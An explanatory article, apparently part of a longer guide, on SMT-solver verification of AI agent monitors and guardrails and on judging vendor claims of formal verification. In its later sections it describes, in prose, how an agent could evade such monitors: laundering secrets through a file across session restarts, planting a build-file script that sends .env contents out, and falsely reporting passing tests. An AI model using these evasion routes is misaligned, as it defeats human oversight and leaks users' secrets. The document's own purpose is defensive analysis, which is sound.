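A quantifier is a phrase such as "for every file" in a formula. Solvers often handle a quantified rule by applying it to terms that already occur in the formula, which can go on forever. For example, a solver that knows `d` is a directory and has the rule "every directory has a parent that is a directory" derives a fact about `parent(d)`, then about `parent(parent(d))`, and so on. Specialists call this a matching loop. Quantifiers also make `sat` answers harder to reach, because the solver has to show that the rule holds for infinitely many values.

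A few well-chosen instances of a rule may be enough to show that a formula is unsatisfiable. If those instances contradict the rest of the formula, the full rule does too, because it only adds constraints. If they don't, the formula could still be satisfiable or unsatisfiable. *Verifiable LLM-Guided Focal SMT Solving for Quantified Arrays* uses this property to let a language model suggest instances. A bad suggestion wastes time but can't produce a wrong `unsat`.

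Nonlinear arithmetic is also hard for solvers. The rule "quantity times price is at most 500" is easy to check when the price is a known number and much harder when both are unknown. No program can decide, for every equation built from sums and products, whether it has a solution in whole numbers (Hilbert's tenth problem). If only three prices are possible, the rule's author can write one linear case for each.

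### Which string queries a program can always decide

A class of formulas is decidable if some program answers every formula in the class correctly after a finite time. For strings, the basic case is the word equation, which joins constants and unknown strings on both sides. Day, Ganesh and colleagues (2018), in *The Satisfiability of Extended Word Equations*, give this example, where · joins strings:

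x · "ab" · y = "a" · x · y · "b"

The solutions are all pairs in which x consists only of a's and y only of b's. With x = "aa" and y = "b", for instance, both sides are "aaabb". In 1977, Gennady Makanin proved that such equations are decidable. The table gives the status of several additions:

| Added to word equations | Decidable? |
|---|---|
| Regular expressions | Yes |
| Linear constraints on lengths | Nobody knows |
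| Constraints on lengths, and conversion of strings to numbers | No |
| An operator that replaces all occurrences | No |
| A test that two strings contain equally many of two fixed letters | No |
| "For every string there is a string such that …" | No |

Day and colleagues proved the results on conversion and letter counts. *Undecidability of a Theory of Strings, Linear Arithmetic over Length* (2016) had already treated the combination of lengths and conversion. The last row comes from *(Un)Decidability Results for Word Equations with Length and Regular Expression Constraints* (Ganesh, Minnes and colleagues, 2013). The question about lengths was still open in August 2025, according to *The Power of Regular Constraint Propagation (Technical Report)* (2025). *Negated String Containment is Decidable (Technical Report)* (2025) settled another question, about conditions such as "the message does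 not contain the key" when both strings are unknown.

The formulas for a plan are usually simpler than the general case. In `path = "/work/app/" · name`, the right side defines the unknown on the left. Ganesh and colleagues call such equations "solved form" and proved that they stay decidable when length constraints are added. *A Survey on String Constraint Solving* (2020) explains that this is because they imply only linear relations between lengths, here that `path` is 10 characters longer than `name`.

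Replacement can be manageable too, if the plan computes each string from earlier ones without loops. Checking such a plan with length constraints is still decidable if it only replaces one fixed text with another. But a plan may fill a template by replacing every `{user}` with an unknown name. According to *What Is Decidable about String Constraints with the ReplaceAll Function* (2017), unknown replacements and length constraints together can express Hilbert's tenth problem, which is undecidable.

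These results describe whole classes of formulas, so a solver may still settle a query from an undecidable class in milliseconds or fail on one from a decidable class. Day and colleagues noted in 2018 that none of the popular string solvers had a complete algorithm. *CloudSec* (2023), which describes a framework for checking cloud policies, reports "performance cliffs" and begins with policies whose only component is a path.

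### Making queries easier

Limiting the length of strings gives the solver a finite number of cases to check. *The Power of Regular Constraint Propagation* lists Kaluza and HAMPI as solvers that translate strings of bounded length into bit vectors. A low limit can make the solver miss a bug, as happened when paths were limited to 11 characters. To prevent this, the monitor can refuse every path longer than the limit, say 200 characters. An `unsat` answer then covers every path that the monitor can accept.

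When a plan has a fixed number of steps, its author can also remove quantifiers. If step 3 is an edit, "an earlier step read the same file" becomes

(tool₁ = read ∧ file₁ = file₃) ∨ (tool₂ = read ∧ file₂ = file₃)

*MANTRA* expands rules in this way, for example the rule that an agent must check the inventory before it assigns a warehouse picker.

If a query remains too hard, the author can split it. Checking 30 rules in one query may return only `unknown`, while checking each rule separately shows which one causes the trouble. *Schwarz* (2026) describes an agent for program verification that splits proofs into small statements for the solver to prove. The agent usually stops a query after 10 to 20 seconds, because a longer wait doesn't reveal whether the formula lacks a fact, contains too much irrelevant material or uses an unsuitable theory. If the author splits a query by the values of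 a variable, such as "dev", "staging" and "prod", the cases must also cover any other value the variable can take.

A monitor can store the solver's answers and reuse them when the same query comes up again. Each answer's key should be the complete formula, together with the solver's version and settings. If the key contains only the tool's name and arguments, the monitor may reuse a permission after the facts behind it have changed. The monitor should not keep time-outs for long, since a busy machine may have caused them.

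Teams should also pin the solver version and replay recorded queries before an upgrade. AWS replayed about 15,000 queries when it wanted to replace the solver CVC4 with its successor, cvc5. An early version of cvc5 solved some queries that CVC4 couldn't finish in 30 seconds, but timed out on others that CVC4 had solved. After a repair to cvc5, CVC4 was still twice as fast on many easy queries, so AWS kept it and added cvc5 alongside it. Amazon Science's *How academic collaboration delivers real-world security to Amazon customers* gives a change to such code, in general, an 80 percent chance of making things better and a 20 percent chance of making them worse.

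Even with the same solver version, reordering the assertions or renaming variables can greatly change the running time. Software that generates queries should therefore always use the same assertion order and variable names.

### Speed at AWS and in agents

Zelkova is the best evidence that solver checks can work on a large scale. *Semantic-based Automated Reasoning for AWS Access Policies using SMT* (Backes, Bolignano and colleagues, 2018) reports that it answered 99 percent of policy questions in less than 160 milliseconds. This is fast for a PSPACE-complete problem, which is at least as hard as any NP-complete one.

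The policy language helps because it has no arithmetic beyond comparisons and can't refer to the length of a string. Zelkova also uses operators that take less computation where it can. It translates a pattern with one or two stars into tests for prefixes, suffixes and contained text, and uses regular expressions only for more complicated patterns. The string `abc` starts with `ab` and ends with `bc` but doesn't match `ab*bc`, so Zelkova has to exclude it explicitly.

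By 2022, Zelkova and the service built on it were generating a billion solver queries a day. Zelkova sent each query to several solvers and used the first answer, which took between a few hundred milliseconds and tens of seconds. It is still in use as the engine behind AWS's Access Analyzer (Buliani, Chunawala and colleagues, 2026, *Prove It, Part 1*). Amazon Science now reports about one billion calls to cvc5 a day, but this figure covers several products and only one solver, so it doesn't show whether Zelkova's use has grown.

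Slow queries may affect agents more than these averages suggest. If a run includes 100 checks, each with an independent 1 percent chance of taking longer than 160 milliseconds, the chance of at least one slow check is 63 percent. A one-second delay hardly matters compared with a language model's response time, but a 30-second delay does.

Direct measurements from agents are scarce. Amazon Science's *A decade of mathematical certainty* claims that AgentCore checks policies "in milliseconds", without giving a distribution. That figure is for evaluating Cedar rules on known arguments, which needs no solver. Agent-C calls Z3 during a task, but the increase in its task times includes the time the model spent rewriting refused calls. With Soteria's limit of 10 seconds per state, verifying a plan with 12 states could take up to two minutes, before any retries.

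### Google's "Inconclusive" answer

Common Expression Language (CEL) is Google's language for short conditions, such as rules for which programs may run on a cluster of servers. *Securing the agentic era* (Google, 2026) introduced a Z3-based verifier for CEL to check policies that AI agents write or rewrite.

In one example, a rule allows ports 80 and 443 only in production. An agent shortens it to `is_prod && port == 80 || port == 443`. CEL evaluates `&&` before `||`, so the new rule allows port 443 everywhere. The verifier returns "Violated" with a counterexample that uses port 443 outside production. After someone adds the missing parentheses, it returns "Verified".

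A third answer, "Inconclusive", is for policies that call a custom function whose behaviour the verifier doesn't model. Suppose a policy allows a program if `signed(image)` is true, and the team wants to prove that only programs from its own registry can run. The solver can produce a violation by choosing an outside program and setting `signed` to true for it, though the real function might never return true for that program. The verifier tracks which results depend on such functions and reports "Inconclusive" if a possible violation relies on one.

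Google claims that this guarantees "zero false positives", meaning that every reported violation is real. The claim is plausible, but it depends on an exact translation of CEL into logic, and Google published no evaluation. A team can test it by running the actual policy on the values in each counterexample. A violation can also be real for the expression but irrelevant in practice. For example, the verifier may report a problem with port 70000 if its constraints don't limit port numbers to 65535.

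The claim also doesn't cover missed violations. Google presents "Inconclusive" as a way to keep false alarms from stopping automated releases. If the release goes ahead, any real flaw involving `signed` is released too. For an agent's permissions, "Inconclusive" should block the change until someone describes the function or reviews the case. The verifier also analyses nested data, such as lists of lists, only to a limited depth, so a team should find out whether "Verified" covers anything deeper.

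AWS similarly says that Cedar Analysis gives precise results without false positives. Cedar doesn't let customers define their own functions, so it doesn't have this gap.

### When the solver is wrong

Solvers are large programs and have bugs. The dangerous error is a wrong `unsat`, because it hides a violation and, unlike a wrong `sat`, comes with no values to check.

Researchers look for such errors by fuzzing, which means running a program on many generated inputs. They compare the answers of two solvers, or construct formulas whose correct answer they know. The developers of Z3 and cvc5 have fixed hundreds of correctness and performance bugs found by fuzzing. Both solvers are now very reliable, but fuzzing can't guarantee that no errors remain. In 2024, researchers published a small formula with two real-valued variables that exposed a critical error of this kind in cvc5.

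One protection against solver errors is to run two solvers and permit a call only if both return `unsat`. Zelkova instead uses the first answer it gets, which saves time but means that an error in any of its solvers can decide the result. Requiring two answers takes as long as the slower solver, and an `unknown` from either blocks the call. It also works only for formulas that both solvers accept, which excludes those with `str.replace_all` when one solver is Z3. Running two solvers does not detect a formula that misstates the policy.

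The other protection is a proof certificate, a list of small steps that leads from the assertions to a contradiction. For two transfers of at most 250 each, it could look like this in simplified notation:

```
1.  x <= 250          assertion
2.  y <= 250          assertion
3.  x + y > 500       assertion (the rule fails)
4.  x + y <= 500      add 1 and 2
5.  false             3 contradicts 4
```

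A separate program checks that the proof's assertions match the original query and that each later step follows from a permitted rule. It doesn't have to search for anything, so it can be much smaller than the solver and easier to trust. cvc5 can write proofs in several formats, including Alethe. *Sundance* (2026), a paper on a simple solver for program verification, cites an independent checker for Alethe called Carcara. If the checker can't verify a step, the monitor should treat the solver's answer as `unknown`.

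Producing and checking a proof takes extra time, which is acceptable for a query that a team runs once, such as one to verify that a monitor handles copied files correctly. When an agent is waiting for the answer, running a second solver with a short time limit is usually more practical.

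## Judging a claim that an agent has been verified

Suppose a company advertises a coding agent as "formally verified to protect your files and secrets". A technical note adds that Z3 found no violation in any run of up to 50 tool calls. The agent works in `/work/app` and has three tools: `read`, `edit` and `post`, which sends text to a web server. Before judging the claim, a buyer should write it out in full:

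> For every run of at most 50 tool calls, if
>
> - the monitor receives every call before it runs,
> - the facts that the monitor uses are true when the call runs, and
> - `read`, `edit` and `post` behave as their contracts state,
>
> then no call
>
> - changes a file outside `/work/app`,
> - sends text derived from `.env` to any server except `ci.example.com`, or
> - edits a file whose current contents the agent has not read.

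If a plugin writes to the disk without going through the monitor, the proof is still valid but no longer applies to that run. The buyer also needs the three rules to express what the company meant and 50 calls to be enough for real sessions, neither of which is in the statement.

The full version also shows what the claim doesn't cover. The agent could still read files outside the project, empty every file inside it, or tell the user a password in a chat message.

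### Testing each assumption

The condition that every call goes through the monitor is an old security principle called complete mediation. A buyer can test it by replacing the monitor with one that refuses everything, then giving the agent ordinary work in a sandbox that logs file changes and network connections. Apart from the connection to the language model, any logged change or connection reveals a route around the monitor. The test finds only routes used during that session, so someone should also list all the code that can write to disk, start a program or open a connection, including plugins and automatic updates, which are easy to forget.

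A customer who uses the agent over the internet can't run this test. A developer who keeps an agent's code private may claim to run a published guardrail with it, but skip the guardrail or run an altered version. *Proof-of-Guardrail in AI Agents and What (Not) to Trust from It* (2026) proposes a system meant to let users verify, without seeing the agent's code, that the declared guardrail ran. Users can't tell from this evidence whether the guardrail's rules are good.

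The buyer can test the facts by trying to make them false. For the path rule, a test program replaces a directory with a link during an edit. For the order rule, it saves a file from another editor after the agent has read it. For the secrets rule, the buyer puts a unique string in `.env`, a backup copy and an environment variable, and checks whether the string reaches a server that isn't on the allowlist. The buyer should also withhold each fact in turn and check that the monitor blocks the call.

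A test of the contracts runs each tool on many generated inputs and compares the whole project before and after each run. For example, if the project reformats its code after every edit, an edit to `a.py` may also change `b.py`, which the agent has never read. If the contract says that `edit` changes only the named file, the solver will miss this violation of the order rule.

To check that the rules match what the company intended, the buyer should write down some permitted and forbidden tool calls before looking at the formulas, then run them through the real monitor. Faulty translations of rules into formulas are common enough that a proof without these tests deserves little trust.

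To judge the bound, the buyer needs to know how long real sessions are. If some have 400 calls, a proof for 50 leaves the last 350 uncovered. The company could restart the session after every 50 calls, but then the monitor has to keep its records across restarts. Otherwise the agent can copy the passwords into `notes.txt` at call 49 and post the file in the next session, where it has no label. An inductive proof covers sessions of any length, but the labels still have to carry over from one session to the next.

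Even if all these tests succeed, the solver could be wrong, or the monitor's program could differ from the formula that describes it.

### Verifying the agent framework

Generating the program from the verified source can narrow the gap between formula and program. In *Containment Verification*, Moon and Varshney (2026) do this for PocketFlow, a very small agent framework (software that turns a model's output into actions). They write the framework's main loop in Dafny, prove that it obeys a policy, and use Dafny's compiler to produce the Python code that runs.

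The proof represents the language model as a function without a body. Dafny must assume that such a function can return any value of its declared type, which here means any action the framework accepts. The result therefore doesn't depend on the model's training or intentions.

The proof compares two state machines. An abstract machine describes safe behaviour, and a concrete one describes the framework. Moon and Varshney prove three facts about them:

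- Their starting states match.
- For every step of the concrete machine, the abstract machine has a step with the same action, a matching outside effect and a matching next state.
- If the abstract step obeys the policy, so does the concrete step.

They also prove that the abstract machine obeys the policy for every sequence of actions. By induction, the concrete machine then obeys it in runs of any length, so the claim doesn't need a limit on run length, such as 50.

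The policy lets the framework read only paths under a workspace directory, call only tools on an approved list, and take only a limited number of steps. The buyer of the coding agent would get a rule about which paths it may read, but no rule about secrets or about reading a file before editing it. The policy also doesn't limit what an approved tool does. Moon and Varshney acknowledge that a framework with a general shell tool can guarantee no more than the shell does.

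The guarantee still assumes complete mediation, which Moon and Varshney call "effect exclusivity". It also relies on Dafny, on the code that converts the model's output into actions, and on a description of the framework that leaves out concurrency and timing. Moon and Varshney tested the compiled program with permitted and forbidden actions, and it recorded only permitted events. But it would still be worth running the test with a monitor that refuses everything, because an effect that bypasses the framework wouldn't appear in that record.

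Language models wrote the specification and the proof. Moon and Varshney hid the code from the model while it wrote the safety property, because a model that sees the code may write a specification that merely restates it. Automatic checks then confirmed that the proof failed both when most of its invariant was removed and when a language model inserted a plausible mistake.

They ran this process on two workflows, and every run passed the checks and the final proof. Even so, one kind of specification was hollow. The second workflow searches documents, and its data didn't fit the template for the safety property. When the model could see the code, it left the relevant field of the template empty. A rule about every entry in that field was then true because there were no entries. A simplified version for file reads shows the problem:

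```
(declare-const inside Bool)            ; the file is in the workspace
(declare-const recorded Bool)          ; the log has an entry for the read
(assert (not recorded))                ; the description never fills the log

(push)
(assert (and recorded (not inside)))   ; a recorded read outside
(check-sat)                            ; unsat: the rule seems to hold
(pop)

(assert recorded)                      ; can the log have an entry at all?
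(check-sat)                            ; unsat: the rule checks nothing
```

Moon and Varshney recommend adding a check like the last one. The buyer of any verified agent can likewise ask, for each rule, for a possible run in which the rule has something to check.

### A certificate for agent skills

A skill is a package of instructions and scripts that an agent can load. Metere proposes a certificate that a skill uses only the capabilities it declares, such as reading certain files or contacting certain servers. The scheme combines three methods:

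- An analysis of the scripts' source code finds every effect they could have.
- A typed interface for tool calls rejects any call that needs an undeclared capability.
- A solver searches for a session of at most K calls in which something changes without a matching approved entry in the log.

The theorem about the solver has the same form as the coding agent's claim. If the search returns `unsat`, no session of up to K calls contains an unrecorded change. Under another theorem, the skill stays within its declared capabilities in sessions of any length if all three methods succeed and the agent's software regularly compares the log with what actually changed. Beyond K calls, this guarantee relies on the run-time comparison instead of the solver's proof.

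The combined theorem states more than its proof shows. Metere's definition of staying within the declared capabilities also covers requests that the software refuses, so a model violates it just by requesting an undeclared capability. The proof shows only that such a request doesn't run, which is the guarantee a buyer needs.

Metere published an implementation with 53 passing tests, but it replaces the methods in the theorems with simpler ones. It searches scripts for text patterns, checks capabilities at run time, and enumerates sessions instead of calling a solver. The theorem about scripts requires an analysis that never misses an effect. A search for `requests.get`, a Python function for fetching web pages, would miss the same function written as `r.get` after `import requests as r`.

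The paper reports that in its worked example, Z3 returned `unsat` for sessions of 100 calls within a few seconds, but the released code can't check sessions that long by default. Once a skill has the certificate, the agent's software stops asking a person to approve the skill's irreversible calls, so a certificate based on a weak check would remove a safeguard. In the same example, however, the analysis of the source code found that a script wrote to a cache directory without declaring it, which a reviewer could easily overlook.

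### Zero attacks and zero false positives

Wu, Zhang and colleagues (2026), in *Provably Secure Agent Guardrail*, report that their Z3-based monitor let no attack succeed and blocked no legitimate action in the scenarios they evaluated. The figures come from a simulated payment system with a daily limit of 500 and 90 cases that a script generated:

| Cases | What the agent tries to do |
|---|---|
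| 30 split payments | Exceed the limit through several smaller transfers |
| 30 rule changes | Raise the limit or its own privileges |
| 30 legitimate payments | Make a payment that the rules allow |

The specification's two main rules are that the total must not exceed the limit and that only an agent with privilege level 10 or higher may change the limit. The agent starts at level 1. As in Soteria's evaluation, the monitor enforces the same rules that define a violation, so a count of zero violations shows only that the enforcement works. An attacker could still do harm within the rules, for example by sending 400 to the wrong account.

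The test for false positives was also easy. The model was told to turn each legitimate request into a payment, without refusing, and had no other tool to choose from. The monitor then had to accept payments that satisfied its rules. The two alternatives tested, a rule checker without memory and a second language model as judge, also had no false positives in nine of their ten results. Even if the 30 legitimate cases were a random sample of real requests, zero errors would be compatible with a true false-positive rate of nearly 10 percent.

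The rule checker without memory couldn't add up split payments, so it caught only half of the attacks with four of the five models that produced results. A sixth model, Claude Sonnet 4.6, produced no valid runs. A fairer comparison for Z3 would be a monitor that keeps a running total and refuses any payment that would take the total above 500. This monitor would give the same answers as Z3 on the split payments.

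Wu and colleagues also describe a longer attack, in which the model Kimi k2.5 tried for 12 rounds to move confidential data from an internal network to the internet. The monitor allowed it to read the data but then blocked it from switching networks. This test is more interesting because the block depended on an earlier step, but it is a single run.

The general proof assumes that every action passes through the monitor, that nobody can alter the monitor's rules, and that each action has exactly the effects that the formula describes. The monitor permits an action when the current state, the action and the rules are satisfiable together. This check works for the payments because each transfer determines the new total. If a formula left the new total unspecified, the solver could choose a value that obeys the rule, as it did for the cancellation of a 30-hour-old booking.

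Wu and colleagues qualify their headline result. They call the experiments illustrations, not representative benchmarks, and acknowledge that the monitor can only rule out violations of the rules someone has written. Their full claim is that in 90 generated cases about one budget, with five models, no payment or rule change broke the budget's rules and no legitimate payment was refused.

### How many requirements can become rules

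Many tests of agent safety have no written rules. Hong, She and colleagues (2026) reviewed 80 benchmarks in *Don't Make Models Guess Security and Safety* and found that 61 percent gave the agent no safety requirements and another 24 percent gave only vague goals, such as refusing anything "unsafe". In one benchmark for customer-management software, the agent should answer a question about whether a sales lead is qualified but refuse a nearly identical question as a breach of privacy. No single rule fits both answers. If a benchmark has no specification, a high score can't show that the agent obeys one.

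Hong and colleagues then went through the policies of three benchmarks sentence by sentence. They excluded sentences that stated no requirement on the agent and asked whether ordinary code or logic could enforce the rest:

| Benchmark | Source of the policy | Requirements | Enforceable |
|---|---|---|---|
| τ²-Bench, customer service | Benchmark's authors | 51 | 42 (82%) |
| CAR-bench, in-car assistant | Benchmark's authors | 18 | 17 (94%) |
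| MedAgentBench, medical records | Language models | 57 | 34 (60%) |
| Total | | 126 | 93 (74%) |

Of the 93 enforceable requirements, 88 needed only simple measures, such as checking a tool's arguments, asking the user for confirmation or using a fixed message template. The other five needed rules about the order of calls or the flow of data. For agents like these, a claim of verification based on an SMT solver isn't necessarily stronger than one based on a few well-placed if-statements.

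The 74 percent is a share of requirements and doesn't measure how much harm they prevent. It also comes from only three policies, one of which language models wrote for the study. For the two existing policies alone, the share is 86 percent.

The requirements that code couldn't enforce concerned the agent's tone, invented information, the order of steps in a conversation, and matters of common sense. In τ²-Bench, for example, the agent must not offer compensation unless the customer explicitly asks for it. Code could block compensation until the customer writes the word "compensation". A solver could verify that rule, but a customer who writes "I want my money back" would get nothing.

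### Harm without a broken rule

The coding agent can do serious damage while obeying all three of its rules. Suppose a user asks it to speed up a slow login page, and it removes the password check. The file is inside the project, the agent has read it, and no secret data has leaked. The rules permit the edit even though it is wrong for the task, because the formula doesn't encode what the user wanted.

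The agent can also mislead its user. It has no tool for running tests, but it can still write that all tests passed, and the user may then release a broken program. Moon and Varshney exclude truthfulness and deception from their guarantee because judging them requires interpreting the text.

Several permitted calls can also cause harm together. For example, an agent could create a script that reads `.env` and sends its contents to an outside server, then add a line to the project's build file that runs the script. Neither edit contains a password, so neither carries a taint label. The script sends the passwords when a developer builds the project the next day, outside the monitor's control. A rule against editing build files would stop this version, but the agent could put the same line in the program's start-up code.

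Supporters of verification reply that a narrow guarantee is still worth having. Moon and Varshney compare it to the control rods of a nuclear reactor, which drop by gravity when the operators lose control, whatever caused the failure. Many of the worst things an agent can do, such as sending out data, moving money or deleting files, require an action that software can check. Hong and colleagues argue that a company needs to rule out certain actions, not just make them rarer. In their tests on τ²-Bench, 20 percent of runs with GPT-5 still contained a violation, down from 52 percent with GPT-4o. Enforcing the rules in code eliminated a large class of violations without reducing the number of tasks completed.

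This reply is convincing for agents with a few narrow tools. If an airline's cancellation tool refuses tickets for departed flights, the agent cannot use it to cancel such a ticket, whether by mistake or because of a planted instruction. The reply is weaker for coding agents with a shell. Hong and colleagues class these as general-purpose agents, and none of the benchmarks for such agents had verifiable rules that applied across tasks.

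Moon and Varshney also argue that their guarantee doesn't weaken as models become more capable. That is true of the theorem, which covers every action the model could request. But the theorem assumes that no effect bypasses the framework, and a more capable model may be better at finding a bypass. They mention a flaw in the Linux kernel that went unnoticed for nearly ten years, and they recommend running even a verified framework inside a sandbox.
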